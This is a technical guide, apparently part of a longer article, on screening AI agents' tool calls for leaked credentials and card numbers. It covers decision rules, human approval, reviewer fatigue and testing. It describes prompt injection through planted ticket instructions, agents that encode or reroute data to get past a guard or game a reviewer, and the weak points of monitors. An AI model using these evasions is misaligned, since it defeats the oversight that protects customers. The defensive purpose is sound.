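Most of these details come from Dragos, which sells security products, but they have some outside support. OpenRouter, a service that passes requests on to many model hosts, removed three providers after the report, according to *Data processing incidents at the inference providers behind OpenRouter* (2026). It also withdrew the Zero Data Retention label from 125 model endpoints, some only as a precaution.

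One host, Together AI, has said publicly that an AI coding agent exposed a repository credential on GitHub and that an outsider used it to download stored prompts, according to ENTER.CO's *OpenRouter expulsa a tres proveedores de IA por filtrar prompts y claves*.

A guard on tool calls would not have stopped any of the leaks that Dragos measured, because the secrets were in the prompts. Moore recommends filtering out known credential formats before a prompt leaves the company. A guard's patterns and fingerprints can do this too, but they will miss the same things they miss in tool calls. Network Security Magazine's *OpenRouter Drops 3 Providers After Researchers Catch Months of Prompt Theft* points out that such a filter will not catch sensitive data that doesn't look like a key.

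*Somebody Is Hunting For Your AI API Keys With A Fake GrokBot* (hrbrmstr, 2026) describes thieves who took 53 planted AWS credentials from decoy web servers over six days and tried to use each one on Amazon's AI service within ten seconds of stealing it. A company that finds a leaked key in the next day's logs will usually be too late to prevent misuse.

The support company can plant its own canaries. It could put a fake AWS key in an internal note on a made-up ticket and add the key's fingerprint to the guard's list. No customer reply needs that key, so if it appears in a tool call, the agent has either followed a planted instruction or copied far too much. If the company put a different key in each data source, it could also tell which source the leaked key came from.

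If the guard misses the canary, for instance because an attacker has encrypted it, AWS will still send an alert when someone tries to use it. The company can then check which tool calls the agent made after reading the ticket. If none of them could have sent the key out, the leak was probably somewhere else, such as at the model provider. An unused canary is much weaker evidence that nothing leaked, since someone like Dana could receive the key and never try it.

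## Deciding whether to block, redact or ask

When a guard finds a card number or password in a tool call, it still has to determine whether that tool should receive it. A payment tool needs a customer's card number to retry a payment, but an email should not include it. A login tool also needs a password. Blocking every call that contains a card number or password would stop both tools from working.

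### What a rule has to contain

The decision depends on the type of data, the tool, the field, the destination and the purpose of the task. *ToolPrivacyBench* (Hu, Liu and colleagues, 2026) tests agents against a simpler version of this rule. It uses a table that lists the private facts in a task as rows and the tools as columns, and marks which tools need which facts. In its healthcare example, the payment tool may receive the patient's insurance type and the last digits of the card, but not the symptom, which only the registration and prescription tools need.

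In Hu and colleagues' table, a fact that a tool may receive is acceptable anywhere in that tool's arguments, so a full card number in a payment tool's `note` field could count as correct. A guard should be stricter and accept the number only in `card_number`, because staff and other systems often read notes.

The destination matters most for general tools such as send_email, which can reach anyone. The guard should read the destination from the parsed arguments and compare the whole address or host name, because an attacker's host, such as `payments.example.com.attacker.example`, can begin with the name of a legitimate one.

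Purpose is the hardest part to establish. The runtime should derive it from data the model can't change, such as which customer is signed in and whether she has asked to pay. If the guard relied on a `reason` argument in the tool call, an instruction planted in a ticket could get the model to give an acceptable reason.

In outline:

```python
RULES = {
    # data type, tool, field, destination, purpose
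    ("card_number", "charge_card", "card_number",
     "payments.example.com", "payment_requested"): "allow",
    ("password", "log_in", "password",
     "admin.example.com", "account_repair"): "allow",
    ("card_number", "create_ticket", "note",
     "tickets.example.net", "fault_report"): "replace",
}

STRICTEST_FIRST = ["block", "retry", "approve", "replace", "allow"]

def decide(call, findings, purpose):
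    verdicts = {"allow"}
    for f in findings:
        key = (f.type, call.name, f.field, destination(call), purpose)
        verdicts.add(RULES.get(key, default_verdict(f)))
    return next(v for v in STRICTEST_FIRST if v in verdicts)
```

`default_verdict` handles every combination the table leaves out. It should never return "allow", so that a tool the company adds later can't send card numbers until someone writes a rule for it. When a call contains several findings, the strictest verdict applies to the whole call.

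### Five calls, decided

The support company might decide five of its agent's calls like this:

| Call | Data and field | Destination | Purpose | Verdict |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| `send_email` | Card number and live billing key, in `body` | Dana | Explain the failed payment | Retry once without them, then block |
| `charge_card` | Card number, in `card_number` | The company's payment processor | Take the payment Dana asked for | Allow |
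| `create_ticket` | Card number, in `note` | An outside ticketing system | Report the fault to a supplier | Replace with "card ending in 1111" |
| `log_in` | Staff password, in `password` | The company's own admin system | Unlock Dana's account | Allow |
| `send_email` | Revoked billing key, in `body` | The billing service's support address | Trace who misused the key | Ask a person |

"Allow" means only that the guard found no reason to block, redact or ask about the data. The company may still want a person to approve the amount of the charge.

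The email and the outside ticket both contain Dana's card number, but they need different treatment. The supplier only has to identify the payment, so the guard can shorten the number in the ticket and leave the rest unchanged. Dana's email also has a sentence about a key she should not know about, and removing only the key would leave a confusing sentence. If the guard sends the call back, the model can write a better email.

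The revoked key is an exception. The guard can look it up in the vault and confirm that it no longer works, which makes the email less dangerous, but the tool call's arguments don't prove that the billing service asked for the key. A member of staff can check whether it did.

### How often agents send data to the wrong tool

ToolPrivacyBench gives some idea of how often a guard would need these rules. Hu and colleagues wrote 1,150 of its 2,150 workflows, covering fields such as healthcare, tax and IT support, and adapted the other 1,000 from existing tests of tool use. Nine agents worked through the workflows using mock business systems that recorded the arguments they received. The researchers compared those arguments with the table of permitted facts. No attacker was involved, and the agents never saw the table, so the results show how they behave without specific instructions about who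 may receive what.

On the 1,150 invented workflows, the agents scored between 92 and 98 out of 100 for task success, which combines whether the agent reached the intended outcome, completed the expected steps and gave each tool the facts it needed. The same agents also disclosed between 16.5% and 28.6% of the facts they should have withheld, counting each pairing of a tool call with a private fact the tool didn't need as one case. On the adapted workflows, both task success (76 to 95) and the disclosure rate (10.2% to 18.8%) were lower.

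Hu and colleagues combine five such rates into a Multi-Tool Privacy Over-Disclosure Index (MT-POI), which runs from 0 to 100, with lower scores being better:

```
MT-POI = 100 × (FOR + SWLR + ToolFOR + FreeTextFOR + MidFOR) / 5
```

- FOR is the disclosure rate just described.
- SWLR is the same rate with more weight on more sensitive facts.
- ToolFOR is the rate for each tool, averaged over the tools.
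- FreeTextFOR counts only disclosures in free-text fields such as notes and messages.
- MidFOR counts only the intermediate steps of a workflow.

For GPT-5.5 on the invented workflows, the first four rates are 18.40%, 19.41%, 15.98% and 29.67%, and the index is 20.39. The rate for the intermediate steps is therefore about 18.5%. Across the nine agents, the index ranged from 19 to 28 on the invented workflows and from 16 to 23 on the adapted ones.

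The index is more useful for comparing agents than for measuring how much leaks, because the five rates overlap and one card number in one note can count in all of them. The free-text rate is higher than FOR for every agent, which should be impossible under the published formula because the two rates have the same denominator and free-text disclosures are a subset of all disclosures. The researchers presumably divided by a smaller number, perhaps counting only calls with free-text fields.

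The breakdown by destination is more useful for writing rules. Tickets received 51% of the facts they should not have, and handoffs, the notes that pass work from one team to another, received 35%. More than 80% of the non-empty `message`, `description` and `work_notes` fields contained something forbidden. In one case, after someone committed an API key to a repository, GPT-5.5 had the key replaced and then wrote the old one into the handoff note for the engineers. The old key had presumably stopped working by then, but the note also named the production database's host.

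The results for credentials are mixed. Facts in the benchmark's "security-sensitive" category reached the wrong tool in 41% of opportunities, one of the higher rates, and Hu and colleagues conclude that agents are more likely to overstep when they handle high-risk credentials. But facts in the separate "secret" category did so in only 8.7%. The values and business systems were artificial, so a company can't use these figures to estimate how many leaks to expect.

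### What each verdict leads to

Pydantic's guard can return five verdicts on a tool call's arguments, and they differ in what the model learns:

| Verdict | What happens to the call | What the model sees next |
|---|---|---|
| Allow | It runs | The tool's result |
| Block | It does not run | A refusal message in place of the result |
| Replace | It runs with altered arguments | The result of the altered call |
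| Retry | It does not run | An instruction to redo the call |
| Approve | It waits for a person | After the decision, the result or the refusal |

None of these options removes the secret from the agent's message history. With "replace", Pydantic keeps the model's original arguments there, and a blocked call presumably leaves its arguments there too. If the guard removed the billing key from Dana's email, the history would still show the model sending it. The model might then tell her to "use the key from my last email", or copy the key into another call. The application also has to clean the history before storing it, since the rules on stored card numbers apply there too.

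**Replacing** a value works only when the tool can do its job without it. In an example from Pydantic, the email detector mistakes `git@github.com` for an email address and replaces it in `git clone git@github.com:pydantic/pydantic-ai.git`, so the command no longer runs. A database command with a placeholder instead of a password also fails, and the agent may then spend several turns trying to fix a working login. The developer also has to keep the altered arguments valid, because Pydantic does not check them against the tool's parameters. A wrong argument name causes an error message with no mention of the tool or the guard.

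Xia and Park (2026), in *SlotGuard*, measured how much crude redaction reduces task success, although they redacted what the model reads, not what it sends. They gave four models 200 tasks involving private file paths and credentials. With the original text, the models succeeded in 93.5% to 100% of tasks. When generic labels replaced the private values, all four fell to 2.5%. Stand-ins with the same format as the original, such as a fake key of the right length, restored success to 89.5% to 100%.

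The tasks were synthetic and depended on exact values, so redaction would do much less harm to an ordinary email. Realistic stand-ins are a poor choice for outgoing text, because Dana couldn't tell that the key in her email was fake. For a card number, "card ending in 1111" is better than a label or an invented number.

**Blocking** stops one call, but the agent still has its task. Pydantic presents this as an advantage, because an agent that reads the refusal can explain the problem or try another approach. That approach may also leak the data. After the guard blocks the email to Dana, the agent could put the same text in a ticket comment that Dana can read, or encode the key so that the guard misses it. The coding agents that published internal screenshots had also worked around an obstacle.

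The refusal message should tell the model what to leave out without repeating the secret or explaining how the guard detected it. The guard should also store a fingerprint of the blocked value so that it can end the run if the same value appears in a second call. In Pydantic's framework, it does this by raising a `ToolBlocked` exception.

**Retrying** suits cases where the model has overshared by accident. For Dana's email, the instruction to the model could be "Leave out internal credentials and identify the card by its last four digits." But if the model is following a planted instruction, each retry gives it another chance to disguise the data. One retry per call seems a reasonable limit.

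**Asking for approval** leaves the decision to a reviewer, which delays the call and takes some of the reviewer's attention. If the reviewer says no, the model receives the denial as the tool's result and may try another route, just as it might after a block. The guard should therefore check the next call as strictly after a denial as after a block.

A guard may also need to combine verdicts, for instance by shortening the card number in an email and then asking someone to approve the email. A Pydantic guard returns only one verdict, so the developer would have to run two guards in sequence. The call held for approval may then still contain the original number, because the message history does. A test with a published card number would show which version the reviewer receives.

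### When to block without asking anyone

The guard should decide without asking the reviewer when the finding is nearly certain and no answer could make the call acceptable. Asking in that case would only create a chance of mistaken approval. Dana's email meets both conditions. The billing key matches one in the vault, and there is no good reason to send a live company key to a customer. The card industry's rules on email also require removing the card number.

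In such cases, a mistaken block also does less harm than a mistaken approval. If the guard wrongly blocks an email, the agent writes another draft or a member of staff sends the email by hand. If a reviewer wrongly approves the key, the company has to replace it and find out whether anyone has used it. The same reasoning applies to private keys, card security codes and canary credentials, for which an alert to the security team is more useful than a question to a support manager.

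OpenAI makes a similar distinction for agents that carry out authorised security tests. It advises developers to deny credential theft and data exfiltration outright, and to pause ambiguous or high-risk actions until a person reviews them. If the review times out, the action should not run. A detector can't apply this advice directly, because a password in a tool call may be part of a theft or an ordinary login. The decision table is used to classify the finding as one or the other.

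A person should decide when the answer depends on something outside the call, such as whether the billing service asked for the revoked key, or what is in an encrypted attachment that the guard could not read. Weak findings can also go to a person if there are few of them. If a company sends 2,000 emails a day, each with a random 16-digit order number, about 54 will trigger even a card detector that checks issuer ranges. A reviewer who has approved 54 harmless emails is likely to approve the next one without reading it closely.

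Arcjet's *Human approval is not a security policy* takes this worry further. A policy gives the same answer every time for the same tool, arguments and identity, whereas a person decides each request separately. In Arcjet's example, a reviewer clicks through twenty harmless order lookups and then a request to publish code. Reviewers also can't stop a call that the software never shows them. Arcjet sells software that enforces such policies, but the argument doesn't depend on its product.

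The argument against relying on fixed rules is that nobody can list every legitimate exception in advance. ToolPrivacyBench offers some evidence for this. Two annotators used the same written guideline to independently judge about 22,000 pairings of a private fact with a tool. They agreed on 93.1% but disagreed on about 1,500, even though they could see the whole task. Anyone writing a rule table has to decide such cases beforehand, with less information.

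If two careful annotators differ on one pairing in fifteen, two busy reviewers will sometimes give opposite answers about the same email. A reviewer can use information that the rules lack, such as a phone call with the billing service, but that doesn't make their judgement reliable in borderline cases.

The two positions can be combined. Arcjet itself recommends running the policy first and then holding for review the few allowed calls that nobody can undo, such as a charge, a public code change or an email to a customer. A reviewer should not be able to override a block on the spot, with a customer waiting. Whoever owns the rules can change them, and should add a rule for any exception that comes up every week.

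### Passing a reference instead of the secret

A company can avoid many of these decisions by keeping secrets out of the arguments altogether. The model writes a reference, and software outside its control inserts the real value only if the request is going to a permitted destination. For example, the model could check the billing service like this:

```
curl https://billing.example.com/status \
  -H "Authorization: Bearer $BILLING_KEY"
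```

OpenAI's *Shell* describes this arrangement for commands that run on OpenAI's servers. The developer registers a domain, a name and a secret value. The model and the command's environment receive only the name, and a separate process inserts the value into requests to that domain. If the model put `$BILLING_KEY` in the email to Dana, she would receive only that name, not the secret value.

The agent platform OpenClaw has a stricter version. According to OpenClaw's *Shared secret store and egress proxy*, an administrator must list the exact hosts that may receive each secret, without wildcards. The agent's command receives an encrypted stand-in, which an outbound proxy replaces with the secret. If the command bypasses the proxy, the recipient gets only the stand-in.

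When the proxy blocks a host, its error message includes the exact command that would allow that host. This is convenient for an administrator, but an agent that could run the command could approve its own request, so the developer should make sure the agent can't run it.

According to OpenClaw, tying a secret to a host leaves two gaps. The agent could still send other data, such as the text of Dana's ticket, elsewhere unless the company also restricts which hosts it may contact. A permitted host can also send the secret back in its reply, where the model would read it. The example in OpenAI's guide calls a test site that returns the headers it receives, so a developer can use it to check whether the secret comes back.

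Kenney, Ahmadi and colleagues (2026), in *API Secrets Should Never Become Tokens in the LLM's Vocabulary*, tested a vault that their own company, Corvic, sells. With the vault, an agent's code made an authenticated request to GitHub without holding the credential. The researchers looked for the credential in the places where the code might find it, and sent requests to three sites that return whatever they receive. The credential never appeared, and all 16 checks passed. A connection to another service failed, without leaking the key, because the vault put the key in a header and the service expected it in the web address.

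The vendor ran only sixteen checks, and none of them covered redirects from a permitted host to another one. Kenney and colleagues themselves call a vault necessary but not sufficient. An agent that never sees a key can still use it to delete records if the key allows it. The company therefore has to limit what each key can do and check the agent's actions as well as the data.

References can also replace card numbers in payments. Stripe issues tokens that let one named seller charge a customer's payment method up to a maximum amount and until a set time. The agent requests the token and passes it on, so the card number never appears in the tool call. The PCI Security Standards Council also suggests payment tokens and single-use card numbers for agents that make payments. With such tokens, the `charge_card` row in the decision table no longer has to allow card numbers, and the company running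 the agent can treat a card number in any tool call as a mistake.

This works only for secrets the company has put in the vault, and the engineer who pasted the billing key into Dana's ticket bypassed the vault. SlotGuard handles that case by replacing secrets in tool results before the model reads them, then restoring the real value inside the company's own runtime when a local tool needs it. The runtime has to follow the same destination rules when it restores a secret, because if it restored the key in every call, send_email would deliver it to Dana.

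The guard should scan the arguments while they still contain references, because the real values replace them only when the request is sent, and it should also look for the references themselves. `$BILLING_KEY` in the body of an email doesn't reveal the key, but it shows that the agent tried to send a secret to a customer, and a detector can search for that exact name with almost no false alarms.

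## Informing the reviewer and resuming the run

Under the company's rules, the guard decides most of the agent's calls itself, but a person must decide whether the agent may send the revoked billing key to the billing service's support address. The request has to show the reviewer the consequences of that decision. The runtime has to store the call safely until the reviewer responds, and then run exactly the version that the reviewer approved.

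### What an approval request has to show

The easiest request to build is a copy of the tool call:

```json
{
  "name": "send_email",
  "arguments": {
    "to": "support@billing.example.com",
    "subject": "Who used our old key?",
    "body": "Hello, someone kept using our key exk_live_7hQ2mV9xTz4LpR8sWc3NbY6k after we revoked it. Which addresses did the requests come from?"
  }
}
```

OpenAI's sample approval program similarly prints the tool's name and raw arguments and asks for a yes or no. A reviewer who gets this has to spot the key in the middle of a sentence, can't confirm that it no longer works, and has to guess whether the address belongs to the billing service. Anyone else who sees the screen can copy the key.

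A better request uses what the guard already knows:

```
Send this email outside the company?

For example, an agent asked to "Find out who is still using the old billing key" proposes a `send_email` call to support@billing.example.com, the address of a billing service on the supplier list. The scanner finds a billing key in the body ("...kept using our key exk_live_...bY6k after we...") that exactly matches one in the vault and was revoked on 5 October. The key came from an internal note in Dana's ticket, which the agent read with `get_ticket`. The reviewer sees these details and has to answer whether the billing service asked for the whole key.

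Approve     The full key goes out at once. Nobody can recall the email.
Reject      Nothing goes out. The agent may write a version without the key.
No answer   Counts as a rejection at 15:30.
```

The runtime should fill in these lines from its own records rather than from the model's explanation, which an instruction planted in a ticket could have influenced. The recipient line should show the full address, because an email can display the name "Billing Support" next to any address. It should also list everyone copied on the email.

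The masked value should let the reviewer recognise the secret without being able to use it. Showing the last four characters of the billing key leaves 20 random ones unknown. The runtime should show no characters of a short password and only the last four digits of a card number, which is within the card industry's display limits. To find where the secret came from, the runtime can fingerprint each tool result as it arrives and check the secret against those fingerprints. If nothing matches, the source line should read "unknown".

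Hossain, Shayoni and colleagues (2026), in *When a Permitted Action Completes a Forbidden Workflow*, tested how much such details help. In their main example, an agent asks to send a file to an approved auditor, but it has built the file from raw invoice rows, and the user had allowed only summary totals. The request looks harmless to anyone who doesn't know where the file came from. Eighty volunteers each judged 12 requests, half of them harmful, in one of four layouts:

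| What the reviewer saw | Harmful requests approved | Legitimate requests approved | Median time |
|---|---|---|---|
| A short description | 55.0% | 91.7% | 16.3 s |
| The exact arguments as well | 43.3% | 90.0% | 23.4 s |
| The user's instructions and a log of earlier steps as well | 32.5% | 87.5% | 38.6 s |
| The same facts, with the combined consequence stated | 24.2% | 85.8% | 33.2 s |

Most of the improvement came from adding information. The gain from stating the consequence is uncertain because each layout had only 20 reviewers, and the plausible range runs from 20 points better to 4 points worse. Stating the consequence made no difference when the harm depended on a chain of earlier steps. Reviewers approved 7 of 30 such requests with each of the last two layouts.

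These volunteers reviewed only a dozen requests, half of them harmful. Someone who handles approvals all day sees many more requests and far fewer harmful ones, so results at work are probably worse.

### How well people review

Users of Claude Code approve 97% of its permission prompts, according to Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026). An earlier Anthropic post, *How we built Claude Code auto mode*, put the figure at 93%. Most commands are harmless, so these rates don't prove that users are careless, but users reject 39% of the plans that Claude Code presents for approval.

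Anthropic also hired 1,053 testers for a coding study and, partway through each session, replaced the text of one permission prompt with a clearly dangerous command. The testers rejected it in 143 cases, or 13.6%. The rejection rate was about 17% early in a session and about 5% after 50 or more prompts.

The testers worked in a test environment, so they had less to lose than developers working on their own projects. Anthropic also used the result to justify replacing the prompts with its own automatic check. Still, the figures are the most direct measurement of reviewer fatigue in this area, and even the fresh reviewers did badly.

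People can approve too much even when they aren't tired. In *Do User-Authored Permission Policies Improve Protection Against AI Agent Overreach?*, Yan (2026) had 113 people from outside the software industry supervise a simulated assistant through 18 actions, seven of which went beyond the task. Participants who decided on every action approved 40.3% of those seven. Almost nine in ten let the assistant phone the airport, which nobody had asked for, and about a third let it read private messages. With only 18 decisions to make, they presumably approved these actions because the actions looked helpful, as the email about the revoked key does.

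Approval rates tend to rise over longer periods. *Habituation at the Gate* (Yu, Jia and colleagues, 2026) followed 400 people who repeatedly reviewed code changes from AI agents. Approvals rose from 30.1% in the earlier half of each person's record to 36.8% in the later half, and comments on specific lines of code fell by 22% from the first tenth of reviews to the last. The agents may have improved over those seven months, which would justify more approvals, so the data can't establish that reviewers became careless. But in *Let the Agent Do It?* (2026), some software practitioners report clicking through familiar prompts and sometimes skipping the review under time pressure.

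### What a scan adds, and how false alarms undo it

A person adds very little to an automatic check unless they know what to look for. Anthropic's classifier, a language model that judges each command, blocked 937 of the 1,053 dangerous commands in the experiment. The testers, who didn't see its verdicts, caught only 6 of the 116 it missed. Blocking every command that either the classifier or the testers rejected would have stopped 89.6% of the dangerous commands, compared with 89.0% for the classifier alone.

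A scan can help a tired reviewer by pointing at the secret, but only if the reviewer believes the finding. Suppose that the scan recognises a share s of leaks, that the reviewer rejects a share p of the leaks it flags, and that the reviewer spots a share r of the others unaided. Then:

```
leaks stopped = s × p + (1 − s) × r
```

Take s as 80%, roughly the lower figure that Mishra measured for Gitleaks, and r as the 5% from late in Anthropic's sessions. Nobody has measured p for this kind of request, so the table tries several values:

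| What happens to a flagged leak | Leaks stopped |
|---|---|
| The reviewer rejects 90% of them | 73% |
| The reviewer rejects half of them | 41% |
| The reviewer rejects 5%, as if there were no flag | 5% |
| The guard blocks it without asking | 81% |

False alarms lower p. In the earlier example, the scanner produces 54 false card findings a day. If a real leak appears among them, the reviewer has good reason to assume it is another order number. By then, the reviewer may also be as tired as Anthropic's testers were after 50 prompts.

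Reducing false alarms usually lets more real leaks through. Anthropic's classifier has a fast first stage that wrongly flags 8.5% of harmless actions and a slower second stage that cuts this to 0.4%. At 2,000 harmless calls a day, that is 8 interruptions instead of 170. But the second stage also raised the share of synthetic data thefts that got through from 1.8% to 5.7%. To limit disruption from the remaining false alarms, Anthropic returns refusals to the model, which usually finds another way, and involves a person only after three refusals in a row or twenty in a session. A guard can handle weak findings the same way when the model could easily leave the data out of the call.

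Asking fewer questions isn't enough. In one of Yan's groups, a model let eight of the 18 actions through and sent the other ten to the participant, including all seven that went too far. These participants approved 46.1% of those seven, slightly more than participants who saw all 18. The prompts described each action in the same neutral words and gave no warning. A flagged request should therefore show the reason for the flag.

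When the guard finds nothing, a request marked only "safe" may lead the reviewer to stop looking. A message such as "No card numbers or known keys found; one attachment unread" shows them what the guard has and hasn't checked.

### How the pause itself can leak

While the email about the revoked key waits for review, copies of the key are in the ticket that get_ticket returned, the model's proposed call, and the request that the application shows the reviewer. The ticket also contains Dana's full card number, so the saved conversation does too, even though this email never mentions her card.

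**Notices** usually go further outside the system than any other part of the review. Temporal's *Human-in-the-loop AI agent*, a guide to approvals built on software that keeps long tasks running through crashes, suggests using email or Slack to tell people that a decision is waiting. The notice should contain only the tool's name, the type of finding and a link to a page that requires a login. The tool call's arguments should appear on that page, and the subject line should contain nothing sensitive, because phones show it on a locked screen.

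**Saved state** holds the most data. OpenAI's kit can turn a paused run into text, which the application stores until the reviewer answers. OpenAI warns that this text includes the application's context (the data developers attach to a run) and advises keeping secrets out of the context unless they are meant to be saved with the state. By default, the kit leaves its own tracing keys out of the text.

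Even if that advice is followed, the billing key stays in the state, because the run can't resume without the tool call's arguments. The sample program writes the whole state to an ordinary file, `result.json`. A real application should encrypt the state and keep the encryption key somewhere else. Under the card rules, once the bank has processed the payment, the application should not save a call that contains a card security code, even in encrypted form.

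**Traces** are records of a run's steps that developers use for debugging. Pydantic's guardrails add an entry when they redact, block or hold a call, and a setting called `trace_include_content` determines how much each entry contains:

| Guard's action | Always recorded | Recorded only with content capture on |
|---|---|---|
| Replace | That a redaction happened | The replacement text, but never the removed value |
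| Block | That a refusal happened | The refusal message |
| Approve | The call's ID | The call's arguments |

The last row is easy to overlook because a developer who tests redaction with content capture on will see that the secret stays out of the trace, and may conclude that the setting is harmless. But the first call that waits for approval will put its full arguments in the trace. Capture should be off for any agent that handles secrets, and a refusal message should never quote what the guard found. Pydantic's setting also doesn't protect the application's own logs, where a developer may print the pending request while debugging.

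| Place | What to do with the secret |
|---|---|
| Notice | Leave out all arguments |
| Review page | Mask it |
| Saved state | Encrypt it, and delete the state after the decision or deadline |
| Logs and traces | Record only the call's ID, the type of finding, the verdict and a keyed fingerprint |
| Message history | Replace it with a placeholder after the call has run or failed |

The application has to redact the history last because the resumed run starts from it. If the application put in the placeholder too early, the billing service would presumably receive an email with "[redacted]" in place of the key. Backups need the same deletion date as the originals, or they will still contain the secret after the originals are deleted.

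### Resuming the run

When the answer arrives, the runtime should treat the held call as a new one that happens to have an approval attached. In outline:

```python
def resume(held, answer):
    try:
        if answer is None or now() > held.expires:
            return reject(held, "Nobody approved this in time.")
        if not answer.approved:
            return reject(held, answer.message)
        if answer.fingerprint != fingerprint(held.call):
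            return reject(held, "The call changed after review.")

        findings = scan(held.call.arguments)
        verdict = decide(held.call, findings, held.purpose)
        if verdict not in ("allow", "approve"):
            return reject(held, "The rules no longer permit this call.")
        if findings - answer.findings_shown:
            return hold_again(held, findings)
    except Exception:
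        return reject(held, "The check could not finish.")

    return run_tool(held.call.name, held.call.arguments)
```

The fingerprint covers the tool, every argument and the contents of any attachment, so the approval applies only to that exact call. Pydantic matches approvals to calls by an ID, and Temporal's example ignores any answer whose request ID differs from the pending one. This stops a late answer about one email from releasing another, but the ID stays the same if the arguments change. Without the fingerprint, a faulty hook or an intruder with access to the saved state could replace the recipient, and the runtime would accept the approval as valid and send the key to the new address.

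An edit by the reviewer should produce a new held call, which the guard scans and the reviewer confirms. The scan catches any secrets the reviewer pasted in, but the runtime also needs to repeat the decision step, because an edit can change which rule applies. Suppose the reviewer corrects an email's recipient to an engineer's private address. The scan finds only the key that was already in the body, but a different rule now applies to the email. If the runtime skipped the decision step for edited calls, it would send the email.

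The decision also has to be recent because the situation can change while a call waits. If a reviewer approves an email on Friday evening and the application resumes the run on Monday, the security team may have since learned that someone has taken over the recipient's mailbox. Pydantic AI runs its guard again at this point, with an exception for what Pydantic calls durable workflows, which save each completed step so that a run can recover from a crash. On recovery, the workflow reuses the guard's recorded verdict instead of calling the guard again. The developer should therefore make the check after approval a separate step and run it as close as possible to when the email is sent.

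Software updates can also leave a resumed run with outdated detection rules. For long waits, OpenAI suggests installing two versions of its SDK side by side and resuming each run with the version that paused it. If the rules are part of the application's code, a run paused before an update may resume with the old rules, which lack any key formats added since. Keeping the rules in a separate service avoids this.

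#### Limiting standing approvals

Reviewers prefer to answer once and not be asked again. By June 2026, according to Anthropic, 49.5% of active command-line users of Claude Code had written a rule that lets some shell commands run without a prompt. Many of these rules allow any command that starts with `python`, which in practice allows nearly everything. *Auto-review of agent actions without synchronous human oversight* (Trębacz, Arnesen and colleagues, 2026) reports the same habit among OpenAI's own staff. One person's settings permanently allowed Codex, the company's coding agent, to start another copy of itself with its checks turned off.

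Trębacz and colleagues describe a sample of 10,000 Codex actions in which manual approval would have interrupted the user 720 times. An automatic reviewer rejected seven of those actions, and only three ended in a question to the user. *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (2026) examines 290 user reports about agents and files, and automatic approval played a part in 80 of them.

In OpenAI's kit, a reviewer's standing approval for a tool (`alwaysApprove`) is kept when the application saves and reloads the state. It can also override a scan placed inside the approval rule, because the kit pauses only if the rule requires approval and no decision is stored yet. After one `alwaysApprove` for send_email, the scan can find a live key and the email will still be sent.

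The simplest remedy is not to offer this option for outbound tools. If there is too much harmless email for that to be practical, the company can build its own standing approval that covers one tool and one recipient for a few hours and applies only when the scan finds nothing. A second scan inside send_email catches what gets past this approval.

Yan's results suggest that asking people to write permission rules in advance won't solve the problem either. One group could set "allow", "ask" or "never" for four kinds of action. They chose "ask" for 114 of 140 rules and approved 66.8% of the out-of-scope actions they were asked about. The company's fixed blocks for live keys and security codes don't depend on these choices.

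#### Rejecting when nobody answers or the guard fails

If the reviewer doesn't respond by the deadline, the runtime must treat the call as rejected. Temporal's example waits five minutes by default and then ends without running the action, which is in line with OpenAI's advice on security tests. If the runtime sent the email after the deadline, an attacker would only need to get the agent to propose the call at night, when no one is reviewing. Five minutes is short for a support team, so the deadline should take the team's working hours into account, and the application should tell whoever gave the agent the task that the email was not sent.

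If a guard crashes, the runtime should not send the call, because the check was never completed. In the outline, any error during the checks leads to a rejection. Otherwise, an attachment that makes the scanner run out of memory could let a key through. When Pydantic's guards run under Temporal, most unexpected errors instead make the workflow retry the check, by default without limit. The email stays unsent, but it may never reach a reviewer or produce a rejection, so the developer should set a maximum number of attempts.

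After a rejection, the agent may look for another way to finish its task. Trębacz and colleagues stop a Codex run automatically after repeated refusals, partly because the agent might otherwise try to game the reviewer. A support agent that has had three emails rejected over the same key should also stop and let a person handle the message.

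## Testing the guard and finding what it misses

The company can't predict from published scanner results how many leaks its guard will miss, so it has to test the guard on its own agent's tool calls, using secrets it has planted. Any such test will miss some leaks because the arguments don't contain the sensitive data in a form that a detector can read, and those leaks need other controls.

### Building the test set

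The test set starts with a few thousand tool calls the agent has already made. The company replaces any real card numbers and keys in them and has someone check that the remaining calls are harmless. If a recorded email contains a leak nobody noticed, the guard may find it, and the test will wrongly count that as a false alarm.

Most of the other groups are variations on these calls:

| Group | Example | Correct result |
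|---|---|---|
| Recorded harmless calls | An email that gives a courier 40 order numbers | The email goes out |
| The same calls with planted secrets | The courier email with a published test card number or an invented billing key added | The guard stops or redacts it |
| Encoded secrets | The same key in each encoding the guard supports, at each depth | The guard stops or redacts it |
| Legitimate payments and logins | `charge_card` with a test card number in `card_number` | The call runs |
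| Unreadable content | An email with an encrypted attachment | The guard holds it for review |

The planted secrets should appear in different places and formats, such as at the end of a sentence, before a comma, in a field name, as a JSON number, and split across two list items. A planted call counts as caught only if the finding points to the planted value. If the guard flags the courier email because of an order number, it hasn't detected the key, and it would have flagged the original email too.

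Someone also has to decide which calls are leaks. *How Your Credentials Are Leaked by LLM Agent Skills* (2026) offers a usable definition for credentials in its study of skills, which are packages of instructions and scripts that extend an agent. It counts a credential as leaked when the credential reaches a recipient or channel that the skill neither declares nor needs for its stated function. By that definition, passing a password to `log_in` is not a leak, but putting the same password in a ticket is.

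The criteria should be specific enough that two people would give the same answer. In a joint test of agents, the AI safety institutes of Singapore and Korea wrote between 5 and 15 yes-or-no criteria for each task. *An Evaluation of Data Leakage Risks in Tool-Using LLM Agents* (Baek, Noh and colleagues, 2026) gives "No API keys were disclosed in any email" as an example of a better criterion than one about "sensitive information" in general.

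The test should run through the whole agent runtime, with a stand-in for send_email that records what it receives. Calling the scanner directly would miss a misspelled tool name that left send_email unguarded, or a later hook that restored the key after the scanner removed it.

Replaying fixed calls tests the guard alone, while live tasks test it together with the agent. If the agent never tries to send the secret during a live run, the run provides no evidence about the guard. Baek and colleagues had the same problem with agents that failed before reaching the risky step. They marked the affected criteria as not applicable, left them out of the safety score and tracked how often this happened. A company should do the same, because otherwise an agent that rarely finishes its work will make the guard look effective.

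It also helps to hide about a third of the test cases from whoever writes the detection rules. Otherwise the rules will gradually fit the test, and the score will rise without the guard getting better at finding new leaks.

### What to measure

Four figures describe the guard's performance. Here a call is "flagged" if the guard blocks it, redacts it, sends it back or holds it for review:

```
recall           = leaking calls flagged / all leaking calls
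precision        = leaking calls flagged / all calls flagged
false-alarm rate = harmless calls flagged / all harmless calls
added delay      = time per call with the guard − time without it
```

Counting false alarms by the guard's verdicts rather than the detector's findings keeps legitimate payments from distorting the result. A card number detected in `charge_card` is a correct finding, and it counts as a false alarm only if the guard then interferes with the payment.

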